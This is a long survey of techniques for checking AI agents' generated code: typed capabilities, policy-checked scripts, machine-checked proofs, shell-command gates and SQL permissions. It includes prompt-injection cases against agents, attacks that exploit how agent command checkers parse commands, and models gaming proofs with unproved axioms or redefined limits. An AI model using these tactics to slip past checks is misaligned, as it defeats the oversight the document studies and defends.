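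The protection didn't make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of ordinary tasks with the containers and 83.3% without them, and MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Sonnet's 83.3% may be an artifact of their setup, because it often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

They also tested TACIT on AgentDojo, an established benchmark of email, banking, travel and chat tasks with injections planted in the data. Across two other models, the benchmark counted one successful attack, in which the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews where the attacker had praised a different one. These results are weaker evidence for the purity rule, because the models' instructions discuss side effects inside functions passed to `map`, and the adapted tools may not have enforced purity. Task completion varied widely. With the model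 o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks, against 81.4% for CaMeL, a system that tracks the origin of data while a program runs.

On τ²-bench, which simulates conversations with airline and retail customers, three models solved between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points more tasks with Scala programs than with ordinary tool calls. At most 7.9% of the programs needed a retry. However, the published signatures of the airline and retail tools include no capabilities or `Classified` values, so this result mainly shows that models can write typed Scala. The tests on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, did involve tracked access to files and commands. MiniMax solved 41.7% of these problems with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

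### Wrong answers, timing and outside programs

Odersky and colleagues exclude three kinds of failure from their guarantee. The first is a wrong result. A script can stay within its capabilities and still count the wrong customers or email the wrong customer.

The second is a leak through timing. A pure function could run longer if a customer's name begins with A, and the script could measure the delay. Each measurement reveals very little, but a patient attacker could take many.

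The guarantee also does not cover external commands, because Scala's types do not apply to a separate program that a script starts. The only limit is the list of commands the script may run. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox, which restricts the files and network addresses that a running program can reach.

The later README adds that `Classified` protects confidentiality but not integrity. By default, a script can put any text in a container and write it over a confidential file, including the file that determines who may log in to a server. Operators can turn off such writes.

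### Checking code inside a running program

In TACIT, the agent sends complete scripts to a separate server. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, instead let a programmer leave gaps in an ordinary Scala program for a model to fill while the program runs. A gap might look like this:

```scala
val open: Int = agent("count the unresolved complaints")
```

When the program reaches this line, the model writes code for it. The compiler checks that code as if the programmer had typed it there, so the code must produce a whole number and can use only the variables, functions and capabilities available at that point. If the check fails, the model receives the errors and tries again. The retailer could make its refund function available at one step of a program and leave it out at the next.

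The generated code can contain further gaps, which helps with confidential data. In TACIT, the model must write the function for `map` without seeing the container's contents. In LACUNA, that function can include a gap, which a trusted local model fills with suitable code after reading the contents. The compiler still requires this code to be pure.

Zhao and colleagues also evaluated LACUNA on τ²-bench, where DeepSeek-V4-flash solved 76.0% of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calling. On the retail tasks, the rates were 58.8% and 80.9%. These differences are sizeable, although the paper describes LACUNA's result as on par with tool calling. TACIT's results on the same benchmark suggest that typed code alone may not explain the difference, although the two studies used different models. TACIT kept the usual agent loop, whereas LACUNA turned each conversation into a series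 of gaps. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the code that DeepSeek wrote for retail tasks and 89% of the code that the weaker Gemini 3.1 flash-lite wrote for telecom tasks.

On AgentDojo, attackers achieved their goal in 8 of 1,898 trials with LACUNA. Zhao and colleagues point out that capabilities do not stop an attacker from making the model misuse access that a task needs. If the support agent can issue refunds, an injected instruction may make it refund the wrong order.

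### Checking each operation as it runs

Amazon's cloud division, AWS, released an open-source tool called Trusted Remote Execution, or Rex, on May 4, 2026. Rex uses a restricted language without an elaborate type system. According to AWS's *Introducing Trusted Remote Execution*, scripts are written in Rhai, a small language with no built-in access to the computer. Rex supplies operations such as reading a file, and each one first checks a policy written in Cedar, AWS's policy language. If the policy does not permit the operation, the script gets an error.

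Because the check happens at the last moment, it can use facts a compiler does not have, such as the exact file a script has chosen. An attacker could still replace that file with a link to another one between the check and the operation. Help Net Security's *AWS open sources Trusted Remote Execution to control what AI agents touch* reports that Rex reduces this risk by continuing to use the opened file, where possible, instead of looking up its name again.

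The drawback is that a script can stop halfway. Trusted Remote Execution's *Scripts that can only do what you allow* shows a script that reads a file and then fails when it tries to write to it. That failure is harmless, but if the retailer added its own operations for refunds and email, a script might refund a customer and then fail to send the confirmation. TACIT and LACUNA reject a script with type errors before it runs, but an accepted script can still fail partway through, for instance if the network goes down.

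Checking operations one by one also doesn't restrict how data flows between them. If a policy lets a script read customer records and contact an outside server, the script can read the records and then send them to the server. Freestone (2026), in *AWS Rex Is a Big Step for Agentic AI Security*, calls data security the most important problem that Rex leaves open. Odersky and colleagues make a similar criticism of sandboxes and address it with their `Classified` container.

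### The cost of typed interfaces

Someone has to build the interface that scripts act through. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the tool descriptions for the airline and retail tests are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the ordinary descriptions they replaced. Agents can draft these, but people need to review them, and whoever maintains the library must understand capture checking. With Rex, the owner of a service writes policies instead, and other teams can change their scripts without changing those policies.

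What the functions allow matters more than the number of lines. The early README shows how to add a database to TACIT with a function that accepts any SQL text. Once a script has permission to call it, the compiler cannot distinguish a query for one order from a query for all of them, or from a command to delete them. A function that takes only an order number is much safer, but the retailer would need a separate function for every kind of question. It would also need a function that looks up a customer's address and sends the email itself, since scripts cannot take the address out of its container.

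To keep the agent from bypassing the interface, the README advises operators to disable its built-in tools for files, commands and the web.

Refund limits also need extra work, because the signature `refund(order: Int, amount: Double)` allows an amount of 5,000 dollars as well as 80. The function still has to enforce the cap. Zhao and colleagues suggest adding conditions to the types, such as requiring a number to stay within a given bound. The compiler could then reject a script unless a verifier proves that the condition holds.

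## Machine-checked proofs about generated programs

A script can come with a proof that it stays within the refund limits, and software can check that proof no matter who wrote it. This approach has succeeded most clearly so far in mathematics, where AI systems now write proofs that would take people a long time to check by hand.

### Proofs that Lean accepts

In September 2026, OpenAI published a proof that, under the Navier–Stokes equations for fluid flow, a fluid at rest, pushed by a smooth force, can reach unlimited speeds in a finite time. OpenAI's *On the Navier–Stokes Millennium Prize Problem* (2026) reports that a group of about 10,000 AI agents found the proof in 88 hours. GPT-6 Astra then took 17 hours to put the argument into Lean, a language for writing and checking proofs. The announcement was controversial, but Quanta Magazine reported that the Lean check gave mathematicians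 confidence in the result. Anthropic had formalised Fermat's Last Theorem in Lean the week before, and according to Computational Complexity's *Navier-Stokes and Lean* (2026), hardly anybody noticed.

In Lean, a theorem is a type and a proof is an expression of that type. Lean's kernel, the small program at its core, checks that the expression has that type, much as a compiler can check that `2 + 3` is a whole number. The expression may come from a person, a search program or a language model. If the kernel works correctly and accepts it, the theorem follows from Lean's axioms, regardless of the author's skill or motives.

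Lean's kernel is part of the trusted base, and it has had bugs. In July 2026 Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous open problem about sequences of numbers. The kernel accepted it because of an error in how it handled certain data types. Lean's developers published a fix an hour after receiving a report, according to their account, quoted by skybrian in *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*. A second, independently written kernel did not have this error, but according to Lean's release notes, Kumar built a proof that exploited a different bug in that kernel at the same time. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a bogus proof that relied on a flaw outside the kernel, in a function that cuts up text. These bugs are rare, but a model that searches hard for a proof might find one of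 them instead. Openwall (2026) advised anyone using Lean for security to recheck existing proofs with the corrected kernel.

Someone also has to read the theorem to see what was proved. OpenAI's proof lets an outside force act on the fluid, so it does not settle what happens without one. Sometimes the formal statement differs from the intended one by accident. Mathematician Terence Tao's *A small cautionary tale with autoformalization* (2026) describes an inequality that Google DeepMind's AlphaProof proved very quickly. The statement contained *n*^(3/2), but Lean treated the division as whole-number division, in which 3/2 is 1, so the proof was about *n* instead. An AI tool had translated the statement, and Tao thought he had probably not reviewed it carefully enough.

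Epoch AI tests models on open conjectures whose statements it fixes in advance. It took most of the statements from a public library and had a mathematician review the others.

### Proof-carrying code

George Necula applied the same idea to software in the 1990s and called it proof-carrying code. A consumer wants to run a program from a producer it does not trust. Here the retailer is the consumer and the model is the producer.

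1. The consumer publishes a policy, such as "no refund may exceed 500 dollars".
2. The producer writes a program and adds any hints the next step needs, such as facts that stay true throughout a loop.
3. A tool reads the program and the policy and works out a verification condition. This is a logical formula that, if true, guarantees that the program obeys the policy.
4. The producer finds a proof of the formula and sends it along with the program.
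5. The consumer works out the formula again from the program it received, checks the proof against it, and runs the program only if the proof is valid.

Suppose the model sends this script:

```python
if price <= 500:
    refund(price)
```

The policy requires *price* ≤ 500 at the call to `refund`, and the script reaches the call only if the test succeeds. The verification condition is

∀*price*: *price* ≤ 500 ⇒ *price* ≤ 500,

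which is trivially true. Without the `if`, it would be that every price is at most 500. That is false, so no proof of it exists.

The consumer has to work out the formula itself because a dishonest producer could send a valid proof about some other program. If an attacker alters the script in transit, the formula usually changes and the proof no longer matches it. If the proof still matches, the altered script also obeys the policy.

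With proof-carrying code, the producer has to find the proof, and the proof checker only has to check its steps. A static analyzer has to judge a script without that help, and Rice's theorem implies that it will sometimes fail. Komendantskaya (2025), in *Proof-Carrying Neuro-Symbolic Code*, notes that the term "proof-carrying code" now also covers any language in which people can write both programs and proofs about them.

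### A refund function with its proof

*AlgoVeri* (2026) explains that a verified program consists of an implementation, a specification and a proof. The example below shows all three in Dafny, a language designed for verification. Its function adds up the prices of returned items, in whole dollars, and leaves out any item that would take the refund over a limit.

```dafny
method RefundAmount(prices: seq<nat>, paidToday: nat)
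  returns (amount: nat)
  requires paidToday <= 2000
  ensures amount <= 500
  ensures paidToday + amount <= 2000
{
  amount := 0;
  for i := 0 to |prices|
    invariant amount <= 500
    invariant paidToday + amount <= 2000
  {
    if amount + prices[i] <= 500 &&
       paidToday + amount + prices[i] <= 2000 {
      amount := amount + prices[i];
    }
  }
}
```

The line that starts with `requires` is the precondition, which the caller must make sure is true. The `ensures` lines are the postcondition, which the function promises in return. (The type `nat` allows only whole numbers from zero up.) The loop may run any number of times, so Dafny cannot check each pass separately. It uses the `invariant` lines instead, which must be true before and after every pass. Dafny generates three main conditions:

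- The invariant holds at the start. The amount is 0, and the precondition guarantees that `paidToday` is at most 2,000.
- Each pass preserves it. If the test succeeds, the new amount is within both limits, and if it fails, the amount stays the same.
- When the loop ends, the invariant implies the postcondition. In this example they are identical.

Dafny sends these conditions to an SMT solver, a program that decides whether logical formulas about numbers, lists and similar data can be true. The solver proves all three without help, so the only part of the proof the author writes is the invariant. Verus does the same for programs in Rust, a widely used language.

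Lean requires an explicit proof, which a model can write. *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* (Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a Rust function that reverses the digits of a number. The verifier translates the function into Lean and turns its specification into a theorem. Claude Opus 5.5 proved a lemma about the loop, using the invariant that continuing from the current state always leads to the correct answer. The whole proof took about two minutes and 150 lines. Anyone can recheck a Lean proof from the file alone, whereas accepting a result from Verus requires trusting its solver.

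The retailer could verify `RefundAmount` once and have every script use it, instead of requiring a new proof for each script. VeriGuard, which researchers at Google introduced in 2025, applies this idea to agents. Before the agent starts work, a model turns the user's safety requirements into a formal specification and writes guard code to enforce them. VeriGuard tests and formally verifies the code, and the model revises it until it passes. The guard then checks each action the agent proposes. The proof shows only that the guard meets the specification, which a model helped write. If the specification is wrong, the guard could still allow an unsafe action.

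### How often models succeed

In 2025, models often failed to write verified programs from formal specifications. In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) reported success rates of 82% in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean. They also reported that success at restoring missing proof hints in Dafny had risen from 68% to 96% in a year, but *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026) explains that the 96% combines the successes of all the models. The best single model reached about 89%.

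VERINA, introduced in 2025, is a set of 189 small programming tasks in Lean. The best model its developers tested at the time proved only 4.9% of the theorems at its first attempt. Later that year, a system from Harmonic proved or disproved 183 of the 189. Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues (2026) report both figures in *Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification* and have resolved all 189 tasks with a system that runs many copies of Claude Fable 5. The copies split up a proof and work on the parts separately. The table compares this with other results from 2026.

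| Benchmark | Given to the model | Model | Result | Source |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| VERINA | Code and specification | Claude Fable 5 | 189 of 189 resolved | Ganguly and colleagues |
| CLEVER | Code and specification | Claude Fable 5 | 113 of 143 resolved | Ganguly and colleagues |
| VeriContest | Code and specification | Claude Opus 5.5 | 1,325 of 1,325 proved | Serbanuta and colleagues |
| AEGIS | Code and specification | Claude Fable 5 | 1,054 of 2,000 proved | Ganguly and colleagues |
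| VERINA | Specification only | Claude Opus 4.7 | 74.6% solved | *P³* (2026) |
| Vero | Specifications for a whole project | GPT-5.5 | 27 of 43 projects completed | Ye, Lou and colleagues (2026), in *Vero* |

"Resolved" includes proofs that a theorem is false, which show that the code or the specification contains an error.

Better models explain only part of the progress. GPT-5.5 solved 13.95% of VeriContest's proof tasks, but with one attempt at each and without seeing the verifier's response. Serbanuta and colleagues let Opus 5.5 use Lean without limit while it worked. A typical proof took 3.4 minutes and cost $1.20. They also tested Opus 5.5 in the original Verus format on the 50 problems with the longest reference proofs. It solved 18 on the first attempt and 49 within ten, although it may have seen the published answers in training.

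The AEGIS tasks are harder because Ganguly and colleagues translated them from ordinary Rust programs, where numbers can overflow and a program can read past the end of a list. Given 30 minutes per theorem, the system proved 66.7% of those from easy problems and 37.6% of those from hard ones. Whole projects are also difficult because many proofs can depend on the same facts, which the model has to discover. In Vero, GPT-5.5 proved 87.3% of the specifications, but those it missed often depended on a few shared facts that it never discovered.

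These systems can easily handle a short function like `RefundAmount` if someone supplies the specification. GPT-5.5 got 48.31% of VeriContest's specifications right on the first attempt when writing them from English descriptions. It succeeded on 5.29% of the problems when it had to write the specification, the code and the proof.

### Weak and impossible specifications

Dafny still accepts `RefundAmount` if its whole body is replaced with `amount := 0`, because the specification limits what the function may pay but never requires it to pay anything. This is acceptable for a safety rule, since a function that refunds nothing cannot exceed a limit, but such a function would be useless to customers. The retailer could rule this out by adding a postcondition that the refund must equal the sum of the prices whenever that sum is within both limits.

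*DafnyCert* (Silva, Amaral and colleagues, 2026) uses this kind of replacement to test specifications. The tool makes small changes to a verified function and looks for a version that still verifies but gives a different output for some input. One function in the VeriEquivBench benchmark calculates how many rungs to add to a ladder. Its specification requires only that the answer is not negative, so a version that always returns 0 passes, even for a ladder that needs 462 more rungs. The benchmark had labelled this specification as strong, meaning that it allows only one output for each input. Among the benchmark's single-function files, 70.2% of the specifications labelled strong turned out to be weak.

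Systems that people verified by hand have had the same problem. IronFleet, a distributed system written in Dafny, carried out each request exactly once, but its specification did not require this. Silva and colleagues recount that when researchers switched off the code that removes duplicate requests, the system still verified. A payment system with that gap could refund a customer twice.

A specification can also be vacuous, meaning that any code satisfies it. Suppose someone writes `requires paidToday < 0` by mistake. No value of `paidToday` meets this condition, so Dafny would accept a function that always returns 5,000. Another verified program could not call the function, because it would have to prove the precondition first, but an ordinary orchestrator would call it without checking. One test is to add a plainly false assertion at the end of the function. If the verifier proves it,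 the assumptions contradict each other. Silva and colleagues note that passing this test does not rule out a contradiction, because the solver may fail to find it.

*VerusEval* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) examined specifications that models had written for Verus. One was for a function that returns the shortest list in a collection. It required the result to have the right length but not to come from the collection, so for the lists [1, 2] and [3] the function could return [9]. Only 42.3% of the programs that Verus accepted passed three further checks without a warning. The checks looked for vacuous specifications, tried examples of right and wrong outputs, and compared each specification with a reference. The last check can raise a false warning, because it warns whenever it fails to prove that the two specifications match. The examples alone rejected 23.6% of the accepted programs.

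The references also contained errors. Wang and colleagues picked out 61 of the 762 references as suspicious, and a review found probable defects in 36 of them. After they restored a missing guarantee in one of these references, 10 of the 11 generated specifications that had failed to match it now matched.

### Added axioms and altered definitions

A model can also cheat on the proof. Lean accepts any declared axiom without proof, and `sorry` stands in for a missing proof. Either one can make any theorem pass. Lean can list every axiom a proof depends on, so the usual defence is to allow only its three standard ones. Rute (2025) suggested as a rule of thumb that each extra axiom makes a proof twice as hard to trust.

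*FORALL-LEAN-AGENT for Auditable Reasoning in Formal Mathematics and Software Verification* (Lwin, 2026) shows how much auditing a proof's axioms can matter. Claude Opus 5 solved all 100 tasks in a benchmark of software proofs under the benchmark's own rules, but only 89 of its proofs used just the standard axioms. With Lwin's software, which adds search tools and a separate reviewer, 96 did. The model was not necessarily at fault, because some of the projects already contained unproved lemmas.

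Auditing axioms does not catch altered definitions. If the specification requires `amount <= limit`, a model could leave that line alone and redefine `limit` as 5,000. Lwin's software rejects proofs that give a new meaning to a name in the theorem. Ye and colleagues take a fresh version of the project and copy in only the parts that a model is allowed to edit. Of the specifications that GPT-5.5 left unproved in their tests, 14% were rejected because its attempts broke the rules.

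It also helps if whoever writes the proof does not write the specification. In Ganguly and colleagues' system, one agent writes each theorem and another tries to prove it, so the second cannot choose an easier theorem. Serbanuta and colleagues tested their specifications against known right and wrong outputs where they could, and had an agent review the rest. They found no errors. In Ye and colleagues' benchmark, a proof that no program could satisfy the specification counts as a valid answer. While they were building the benchmark, this rule exposed several errors that human reviewers had missed.

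### False assumptions about the environment

The proof of `RefundAmount` assumes that `paidToday` is accurate. If the payment record is out of date, or two refunds run at the same time, the retailer can exceed the daily limit even though the proof is correct. No check of the function would reveal this, because the error is in its input.

The software beneath a verified program can fail too. In the Hacker News thread *Lean proved this program correct; then I found a bug* (2026), a commenter quotes the author's conclusion about two bugs in a program verified with Lean. One let an attacker make the program stop working, which no specification had ruled out. The other was a memory error in the runtime, which the proofs had assumed to be correct.

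Specifications also often omit running time. *P³* points out that programs that take exponential time can meet the specifications in VERINA, because those specifications cover only the output.

### Cryptographic certificates for actions

So far the retailer has checked proofs about its own agent. A payment company might also want to check that a refund follows the retailer's rules without seeing the retailer's customer records. To allow this, Gabbay proposes attaching a short cryptographic proof to each action.

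The policy's author writes it as a logical formula, and a compiler turns the formula into polynomials whose value is 0 if the formula is true and positive if it is false:

- *a* = *b* becomes (*a* − *b*)².
- "Both conditions hold" becomes the sum of their values, since a sum of non-negative numbers is 0 only if every one of them is.
- "At least one condition holds" becomes the product.
- A range check, such as *amount* ≤ 500, has the value 0 if it succeeds and 1 if it fails.

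If the agent has already paid out 1,000 dollars that day, a refund of 620 dollars gives 1 on the single-refund check and 0 on the daily-total check. The sum is 1, so the refund breaks the policy. A refund of 80 dollars gives 0 on both checks.

The agent, or a program acting for it, then produces a proof that there is some private data *w* for which

*R*(*pub*, *w*) = 0,

where *R* is the compiled policy for this action and *pub* is the public data. The payment company checks the proof with a key it has approved in advance. It does not have to repeat the calculation, and it need not learn *w*. There is a very small chance that a false proof passes.

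The proof shows only that suitable data exists. If the agent could choose the day's total as part of *w*, it could always choose zero. The total therefore has to be in the public data, or the policy has to tie it to a record that the agent cannot change. Gabbay's paper sets out the mathematics but does not measure how long such proofs would take to produce. The retailer can check its own refund limits by comparing the numbers.

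### A claimed limit on fixed verifiers

Hasan (2026), in *Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity*, argues that proofs for individual actions are necessary because no fixed verifier can certify all safe behaviour. The argument uses Kolmogorov complexity. The complexity *K*(*x*) of a string *x* is the length of the shortest program that prints it. Let *x* encode an input, the AI system's output and the policy, and let *P*(*x*) mean that the output obeys the policy. Hasan proves that for any sound formal system and any large enough *n*, the system cannot prove a statement of the form

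*P*(*x*) ∧ *K*(*x*) > *n*.

Suppose the system could prove, for a large number *n*, that no program of length *n* or less can print a particular string *x*. A short program could then search all possible proofs until it found one of such a statement, and print the *x* in it. This program needs to contain only the rules of the system and the number *n*, so its length grows like log *n*. Once *n* is large enough, the program is shorter than *n* but prints a string that supposedly no program of length *n* or less can print, which is a contradiction.

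Hasan concludes that a fixed verifier cannot certify every compliant case above a certain complexity. The theorem does not support this conclusion, because it concerns proofs that a case is both compliant and complex. The difficulty comes from proving complexity, which Gregory Chaitin showed in the 1970s to be impossible beyond some bound. A retailer does not need to prove that a customer's message is complex. A checker that compares the refund with 500 dollars gives the right answer however long and random the message is.

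Hasan proposes attaching a proof to each case, so that the verifier only has to check it. This is a sensible design, but if the limit were real, it would still apply. Hasan already defines verification as the existence of a proof that the system accepts, and an attached proof has to be written in some such system.

The retailer also doesn't need a proof for every harmless script, because it can reject a script that has none and ask the model for another. In *GenOS*, Priami (2026) proves that if a sound checker must approve every program before it takes effect, every program that takes effect meets its specification, however unreliable the model is. If each attempt succeeds with probability at least *p*, regardless of how earlier attempts went, the chance that *n* attempts all fail is at most (1 − *p*)^*n*. With *p* = 0.7, five attempts all fail less than once in 400 cases.

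A model can also improve its chances of completing a proof by writing a program that is easier to verify. Ye and colleagues found five cases in which an agent replaced a complicated algorithm with a simpler, slower one. The agents proved all 250 specifications for these programs, compared with 201 when they had to use the original code.

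## Shell commands and database queries

The retailer's agent often writes something shorter than a script, such as a single shell command to search a log file or a single SQL query to look up an order. These commands and queries are hard to check because so much of their effect depends on other software.

### What the text leaves out

A shell is a program that reads a line of text and starts the programs named in it. Bash, the usual shell on Linux, first applies its own rules to the line. In `cat *.txt`, it replaces `*.txt` with the names of all matching files before it starts `cat`, which prints their contents. A checker that parses the line differently from Bash may not arrive at the command that Bash runs.

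Each program then interprets its own arguments. The option `-r` makes `sort` reverse its order, but makes `rm` delete a folder and everything in it. A command's effect also depends on the state of the machine. For example, the current folder determines which file `rm report.csv` deletes.

SQL has the same difficulties. The database uses its own parser, a function in the query may do more than its name suggests, and the result depends on the stored data. Even the name `orders` may refer to a view, a stored query that draws on other tables.

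Li (2026) found in *ParseGap* that the command checkers in production coding agents can interpret a command differently from the shell that runs it. A checker's verdict therefore applies only to its own interpretation of the command, and a shell that parses the original text again may run something else.

### ShellPlan

Li's remedy, ShellPlan, removes the second parse. Suppose the support agent wants the refund entries from a log, in reverse order:

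`grep refund returns.log | sort -r`

1. ShellPlan parses the line into a typed plan, a tree that records each program, its arguments and how the programs connect. Here the plan contains `grep` with two arguments, `sort` with one option, and a pipe that passes the output of `grep` to `sort`. ShellPlan supports only part of Bash's syntax and refers everything else to a person.
2. It checks that the policy permits each program, and compares the arguments with a specification of what that program may receive. It also checks any files that the line would read from or write to.
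3. It fills in variables and matching file names, then checks the arguments again.
4. It starts each program through `execve`, a system call that takes a program and a list of separate arguments. No shell sees the text.

The specifications list the permitted options, and ShellPlan refuses the rest. A list of forbidden options would let through any dangerous option its author overlooked. Li tried 55 attacks that relied only on how ordinary programs treat their arguments. An early prototype of ShellPlan without the specifications admitted 32 of them, and the finished version admitted none.

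Li proves two theorems about the design. The first is that if ShellPlan refuses a line, it starts none of the programs in it, and if it accepts the line, it directly starts only programs in the plan that have passed every check. In both cases it may also run a few fixed, read-only probes. The second is that if every program in the plan has a specification, the plan can write only to permitted targets and a few housekeeping files.

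The second theorem assumes that software and settings outside the project folder are trustworthy, and that each program behaves as specified. Li tested part of the assumption about program behavior by checking the specifications of 1,213 options against the real programs. The specifications were always right about whether an option takes the next word as its value, though an earlier round had found nine errors. Audits of earlier versions of ShellPlan found 33 faults, 14 of them security problems, so the implementation also belongs in the trusted base.

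The guarantee does not cover confidentiality. An approved command might still read a file outside the project folder, so the retailer would need another way to block access to customer records.

### What ShellPlan blocks and refuses

Under read-only policies, ShellPlan allowed none of 4,174 attacks in six test suites. Li also had ten models carry out tasks with different gates between the model and the shell. Commands that ShellPlan referred to a person failed because nobody was available to approve them, so the model had to find another way.

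| Gate | Successful attacks (of 90) | Harmless tasks completed (of 100) | Median delay per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 62 | 93 | 0 ms |
| Language model as judge | 6 | 87 | 6,062 ms |
| ShellPlan | 0 | 74 | 1.28 ms |

The drop from 93 to 74 tasks came mostly from weaker models. The six strongest went from completing all 60 of their tasks without a gate to 56 with ShellPlan, while the other four went from 33 of 40 to 18. The test was also deliberately difficult for ShellPlan, because 40 of the 100 tasks asked for shell features it does not support. The six strongest models completed all 36 of their tasks that did not ask for those features.

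Records of real coding agents show more clearly what ordinary work ShellPlan refuses. It accepted 343 of 456 read-only steps in one collection and none of 108 in another, where every command began with `cd`, which changes the current folder. ShellPlan does not support `cd` because it would have to track the current folder to interpret the rest of the line. Together, `cd` and `nl`, which numbers the lines of a file, accounted for 198 of the 221 refusals. Li suggests adding support for both.

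ShellPlan also has to reproduce Bash's behaviour. Its results matched Bash's exactly in all 343 comparisons on the first collection, but in a broader set of commands one harmless line printed the wrong text. This error did not breach the policy, because ShellPlan ran the same plan it had checked.

### CARE

ShellPlan accepts only what its specifications cover. Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *CARE*, instead estimate how risky a command is. CARE puts the command in a standard form, parses it and gives it four scores between 0 and 1:

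- *s*₁ for the kind of action, from harmless reading to destruction
- *s*₂ for the files involved, with writing to a system file scoring higher than reading it
- *s*₃ for matches with 139 rules, most of them from public catalogues of attack techniques
- *s*₄ for suspicious structure.

The total is

0.3*s*₁ + 0.3*s*₂ + 0.3*s*₃ + 0.1*s*₄.

CARE allows a command with a total score below 0.15 and blocks one with a score of 0.35 or more. If the score is between those thresholds, CARE blocks the command when one piece of evidence is strong enough by itself, such as access to a file of secrets. It sends the remaining commands to a language model. In one example, a dangerous command scored 0.6 for the kind of action and 0 on everything else. Its total was 0.18, so it went to the model, which blocked it.

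Liu and colleagues tested CARE on 220 dangerous and 329 safe commands. It caught 75.91% of the dangerous ones and blocked 0.91% of the safe ones, with an average delay of 2.32 milliseconds. Its F1 score, which combines precision and recall, was 85.64%, compared with 73.09% for the best of the other guards they tested.

The language model contributed little to this result. CARE consulted it on 23 of the 549 commands, and the only effect was that CARE blocked three safe commands instead of six. On 600 commands that the same model had written from attack instructions, consulting it made CARE stop fewer attacks. Without a guard, 74.83% of these commands ran successfully in a test container. CARE's rules alone reduced this to 37.33%, but with the model's help the figure was 52.50%. Liu and colleagues think the model may have been lenient because it had written the commands itself.

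A retailer should also consider how rare dangerous commands are. If 1% of 10,000 commands were dangerous, CARE would stop about 76 of them, miss 24 and block about 90 harmless ones, so more than half of the commands it blocked would be harmless. CARE also passes approved commands to an ordinary shell, which may interpret them differently from CARE.

### The sandbox as a second layer

ShellPlan and CARE are both meant to work alongside an operating-system sandbox. When a running program tries to open a file or a network connection, the kernel checks whether the sandbox permits it, and the same limits apply to any other programs the program starts. Because the sandbox does not interpret the command, a misread command can still do only what the sandbox allows.

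Li ran 116 attacks in the read-only sandbox of Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent, without relying on its command checker. None made a lasting change to a file. But an agent that can't write files is of limited use, and a sandbox that allows writes to a folder cannot distinguish a useful edit there from a harmful one. The sandbox and the command checker also need to be independent. ShellPlan never loosens the sandbox for a command it has approved, so a mistake in one layer does not disable the other.

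The retailer could use a sandbox to block every network address except those its scripts need. Blocking the payment service would stop scripts from bypassing the refund checker. But the scripts must be able to reach the database, and the sandbox cannot check which rows a query retrieves.

### Tables, columns and statement types

A checker for SQL starts by parsing the query into a syntax tree. It can then reject anything other than a single `SELECT` statement, which rules out direct commands to change or delete data. It can also compare the tables and columns in the tree with a list.

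Fei and Yang (2026), in *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control*, state the comparison precisely. A policy Π is a set of permitted triples, each consisting of a table, a column and an operation. Perm(*q*) is the set of triples that a query *q* needs. The checker accepts the query if

Perm(*q*) ⊆ Π.

For `SELECT status FROM orders WHERE id = 4417`, Perm(*q*) contains (orders, status, SELECT) and (orders, id, SELECT). The second is there because a query also reads the columns it uses to filter, sort or join rows.

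The checker might still parse a query differently from the database. The retailer can guard against this by giving the agent a database account with read-only access to only the columns it needs. The database then enforces those permissions on the same interpretation of the query that it executes. ShellPlan has the same advantage over a checker in front of a shell.

Telling the model about the permissions is not enough to enforce them. Fei and Yang paired questions about 53 databases with users' roles to make 21,502 cases. The models, all from 2025 or earlier, received the role's permissions in the prompt and had to write a permitted query or refuse. The table shows how often three of them wrote a query when they should have refused, or wrote one that broke the policy.

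| | Spider | BIRD | LiveSQLBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 2.6% | 10.5% | 17.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4.9% | 7.7% | 13.3% |
| Snowflake-Arctic-R1-7B | 48.7% | 65.1% | 82.0% |
| Cases that call for refusal | 47% | 65% | 76% |

Snowflake's model, which specialises in SQL, hardly ever refused (last row). Not all of these violations would leak data, because some are queries that use only permitted columns to answer a question that needs forbidden ones. These would give the user a misleading answer. On BIRD, about two thirds of GPT-5-mini's violations were of this kind.

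Hiding the forbidden columns from the model did not solve the problem either. GPT-5-mini's violation rate on BIRD rose from 12.7% to 26.8%. It answered more questions that it should have refused, and it guessed the names of forbidden columns more often than it had used them when it could see them.

Some leaks involve no forbidden column. Fei and Yang give the example of a user who is not allowed to see salaries but can calculate them from hourly wages and hours worked.

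### A query without the customer filter

Permissions on columns cannot keep customers' orders apart, because all of them are in the same table. Suppose customer 88 asks the support agent three questions, and it writes these queries:

```sql
-- How many of my orders are late?
SELECT COUNT(*) FROM orders WHERE status = 'late';

-- How long do people usually wait for a delivery?
SELECT AVG(delivery_days) FROM orders;

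-- Which products has nobody ordered yet?
SELECT name FROM products
WHERE id NOT IN (SELECT product_id FROM orders);
```

None of them is limited to customer 88. Taint analysis would not help, because none contains any text from the customer.

The retailer's checker could require the condition `customer_id = 88` wherever a query uses `orders`, taking the number from the customer's login. The condition must apply to every row, so the checker cannot accept it as one side of an `OR`. This checker rejects all three queries and gives the model the reason. The model can repair the first by adding the condition. The other two are about all customers, so the agent should reply that it can't answer them.

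The alternative is row-level security, in which the database itself hides the rows a user may not see. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, the retailer could write:

```sql
ALTER TABLE orders ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer')::int);
```

The orchestrator sets `app.customer` to 88 before it runs the agent's queries, and all three run without an error. The first gives the right answer. The second gives the average wait for customer 88's orders only, which the agent would probably present as the average for all customers. The third lists every product that customer 88 has not ordered, including the retailer's bestsellers.

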